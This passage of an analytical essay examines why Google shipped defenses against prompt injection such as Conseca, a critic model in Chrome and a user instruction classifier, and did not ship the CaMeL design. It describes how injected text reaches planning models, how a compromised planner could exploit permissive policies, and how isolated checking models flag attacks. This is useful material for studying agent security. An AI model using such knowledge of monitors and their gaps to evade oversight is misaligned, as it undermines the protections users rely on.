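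*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) raises two further objections. Conseca's guarantees assume that the model writing the policy is safe, and a compromised planner could look for harmful actions that the policy happens to allow. CaMeL also has to trust the model that writes its plan, but the tools' output never reaches that model, so an attacker has much less chance of taking it over.

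Google now uses Conseca in its Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform, according to UMass Amherst. *Surviving the Perfect Storm*, the resource page for Lidzborski's talk on Workspace security, lists Conseca and the layered-defense post but not CaMeL. This suggests that Google favored a defense it could add to existing agents, although the page contains no explanation of the choice.

### Integration as future work

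Shi and colleagues make the most direct statement about how CaMeL relates to Gemini's other defenses. They call adversarial training "necessary but insufficient" and say developers should never rely on it alone when deploying a model. They say system-level defenses such as CaMeL can "complement" adversarial training because a deployed model may still act against the user's wishes. In their conclusion, they leave the question of how to combine the two to future work.

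Four of the report's authors had also worked on CaMeL, so they knew the design well. The report doesn't call CaMeL too costly or unsuitable for Gemini, but it doesn't announce a plan to add it either.

Shi and colleagues did test one defense that isolates a model in a different way. Their *user instruction classifier* is a separate model that receives the user's request and Gemini's response, but not the emails or documents that Gemini read. It flags an attack if the response seems implausible for that request. Chrome's critic later used a similar approach to check actions, although neither Shi and colleagues nor Parker connects the two.

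Shi and colleagues call the classifiers' results against non-adaptive attacks middling, but they still used the user instruction classifier to select training examples for Gemini 2.5. So by May 2025, Google's researchers could already keep an attacker's text out of a checking model's input without changing how Gemini planned.

Timing and engineering effort may explain much of why Google did not ship CaMeL whole in 2025. The robustness report appeared only two months after the CaMeL paper, and Google could add attack examples to the training it was already doing, whereas using CaMeL would have meant rebuilding how the assistant plans. This is an inference about Google's priorities, and it is less convincing for late 2026 because Google had by then had more than a year to do that work.

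### What the product teams wanted

In the Chrome post, Parker credits CaMeL as a partial inspiration for the critic but doesn't explain why Google took only part of the design. Parker acknowledges that the critic has less context than the planner, but argues that its job is simpler because it only approves or rejects actions. A planner that couldn't see the page would lack the same context and have a much harder job.

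Parker also writes that the team planned to tune the first website limits in Agent Origin Sets to "reduce unnecessary friction while improving security". The remark isn't about CaMeL, but a team concerned about friction from a list of websites would have had more reason to worry about a planner that must foresee everything a page might show.

The most convincing explanation for Chrome is therefore that CaMeL fits open-ended tasks poorly, since a browsing agent constantly meets pages that nobody planned for. The low first-attempt score of CaMeL's computer-use version supports this, but Foerster and colleagues published that score after the Chrome post, so the published figure can't have influenced the original design.

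The Workspace team had a different concern. Gavish values quick configuration fixes. Google could edit CaMeL's policies just as quickly, but replacing Gemini's planner would take more than a configuration change.

Neither Gavish nor Quinney mentions CaMeL, nor does Google DeepMind in its post on Gemini 2.5's security. We can infer little from this, because product posts rarely discuss designs the product doesn't use.

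Lidzborski's talk shows that at least one Workspace engineer was sympathetic to CaMeL's central idea. According to *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google*, an audience member suggested sending prompts and data through structurally separate channels. Lidzborski agreed that the industry was repeating an old mistake, saying "we are back in the time of Windows 95", and called for systems that are secure by design. The notes don't record why Workspace lacks that separation, and their references to CaMeL are the note-taker's, not Lidzborski's.

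The role of computing cost is harder to assess. CaMeL's extra tokens would be expensive at Google's scale, but the Chrome team accepted a similar kind of expense when it added a second model to check every action and a classifier to check every page. Cost may have counted against CaMeL but probably wasn't enough to rule it out.

### A co-author's departure

Ilia Shumailov, who co-wrote both the CaMeL paper and the robustness report, had left Google DeepMind by October 2025. In *Is it even possible to defend AI agents against attacks in practice?*, the announcement of a talk at Cambridge, Shumailov (2025) wrote that prompt injections make AI agents hard to deploy. According to the biography in the announcement, Shumailov now runs sequrity.ai, which builds tools to secure AI agents.

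Shumailov therefore has a commercial interest in persuading developers that agents need more protection than model training can provide. The later studies that Shumailov co-wrote, by Foerster and colleagues and by Peters-Gill and colleagues, report serious weaknesses in CaMeL, but a company that sells security tools can benefit from finding weaknesses as well as from fixing them. Google also has an interest in presenting the defenses it already ships as sound.

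The talk announcement gives no reason for Shumailov's departure, so it isn't evidence of a dispute over CaMeL. Shumailov may have said more in recorded conversations, such as Machine Learning Street Talk's *AI Agents Can Code 10,000 Lines of Hacking Tools In Seconds* (2025), an hour-long interview from the same month. CaMeL's influence at Google outlasted Shumailov's time there. Parker cited CaMeL in December 2025, and Berschadski cited it in August 2026.
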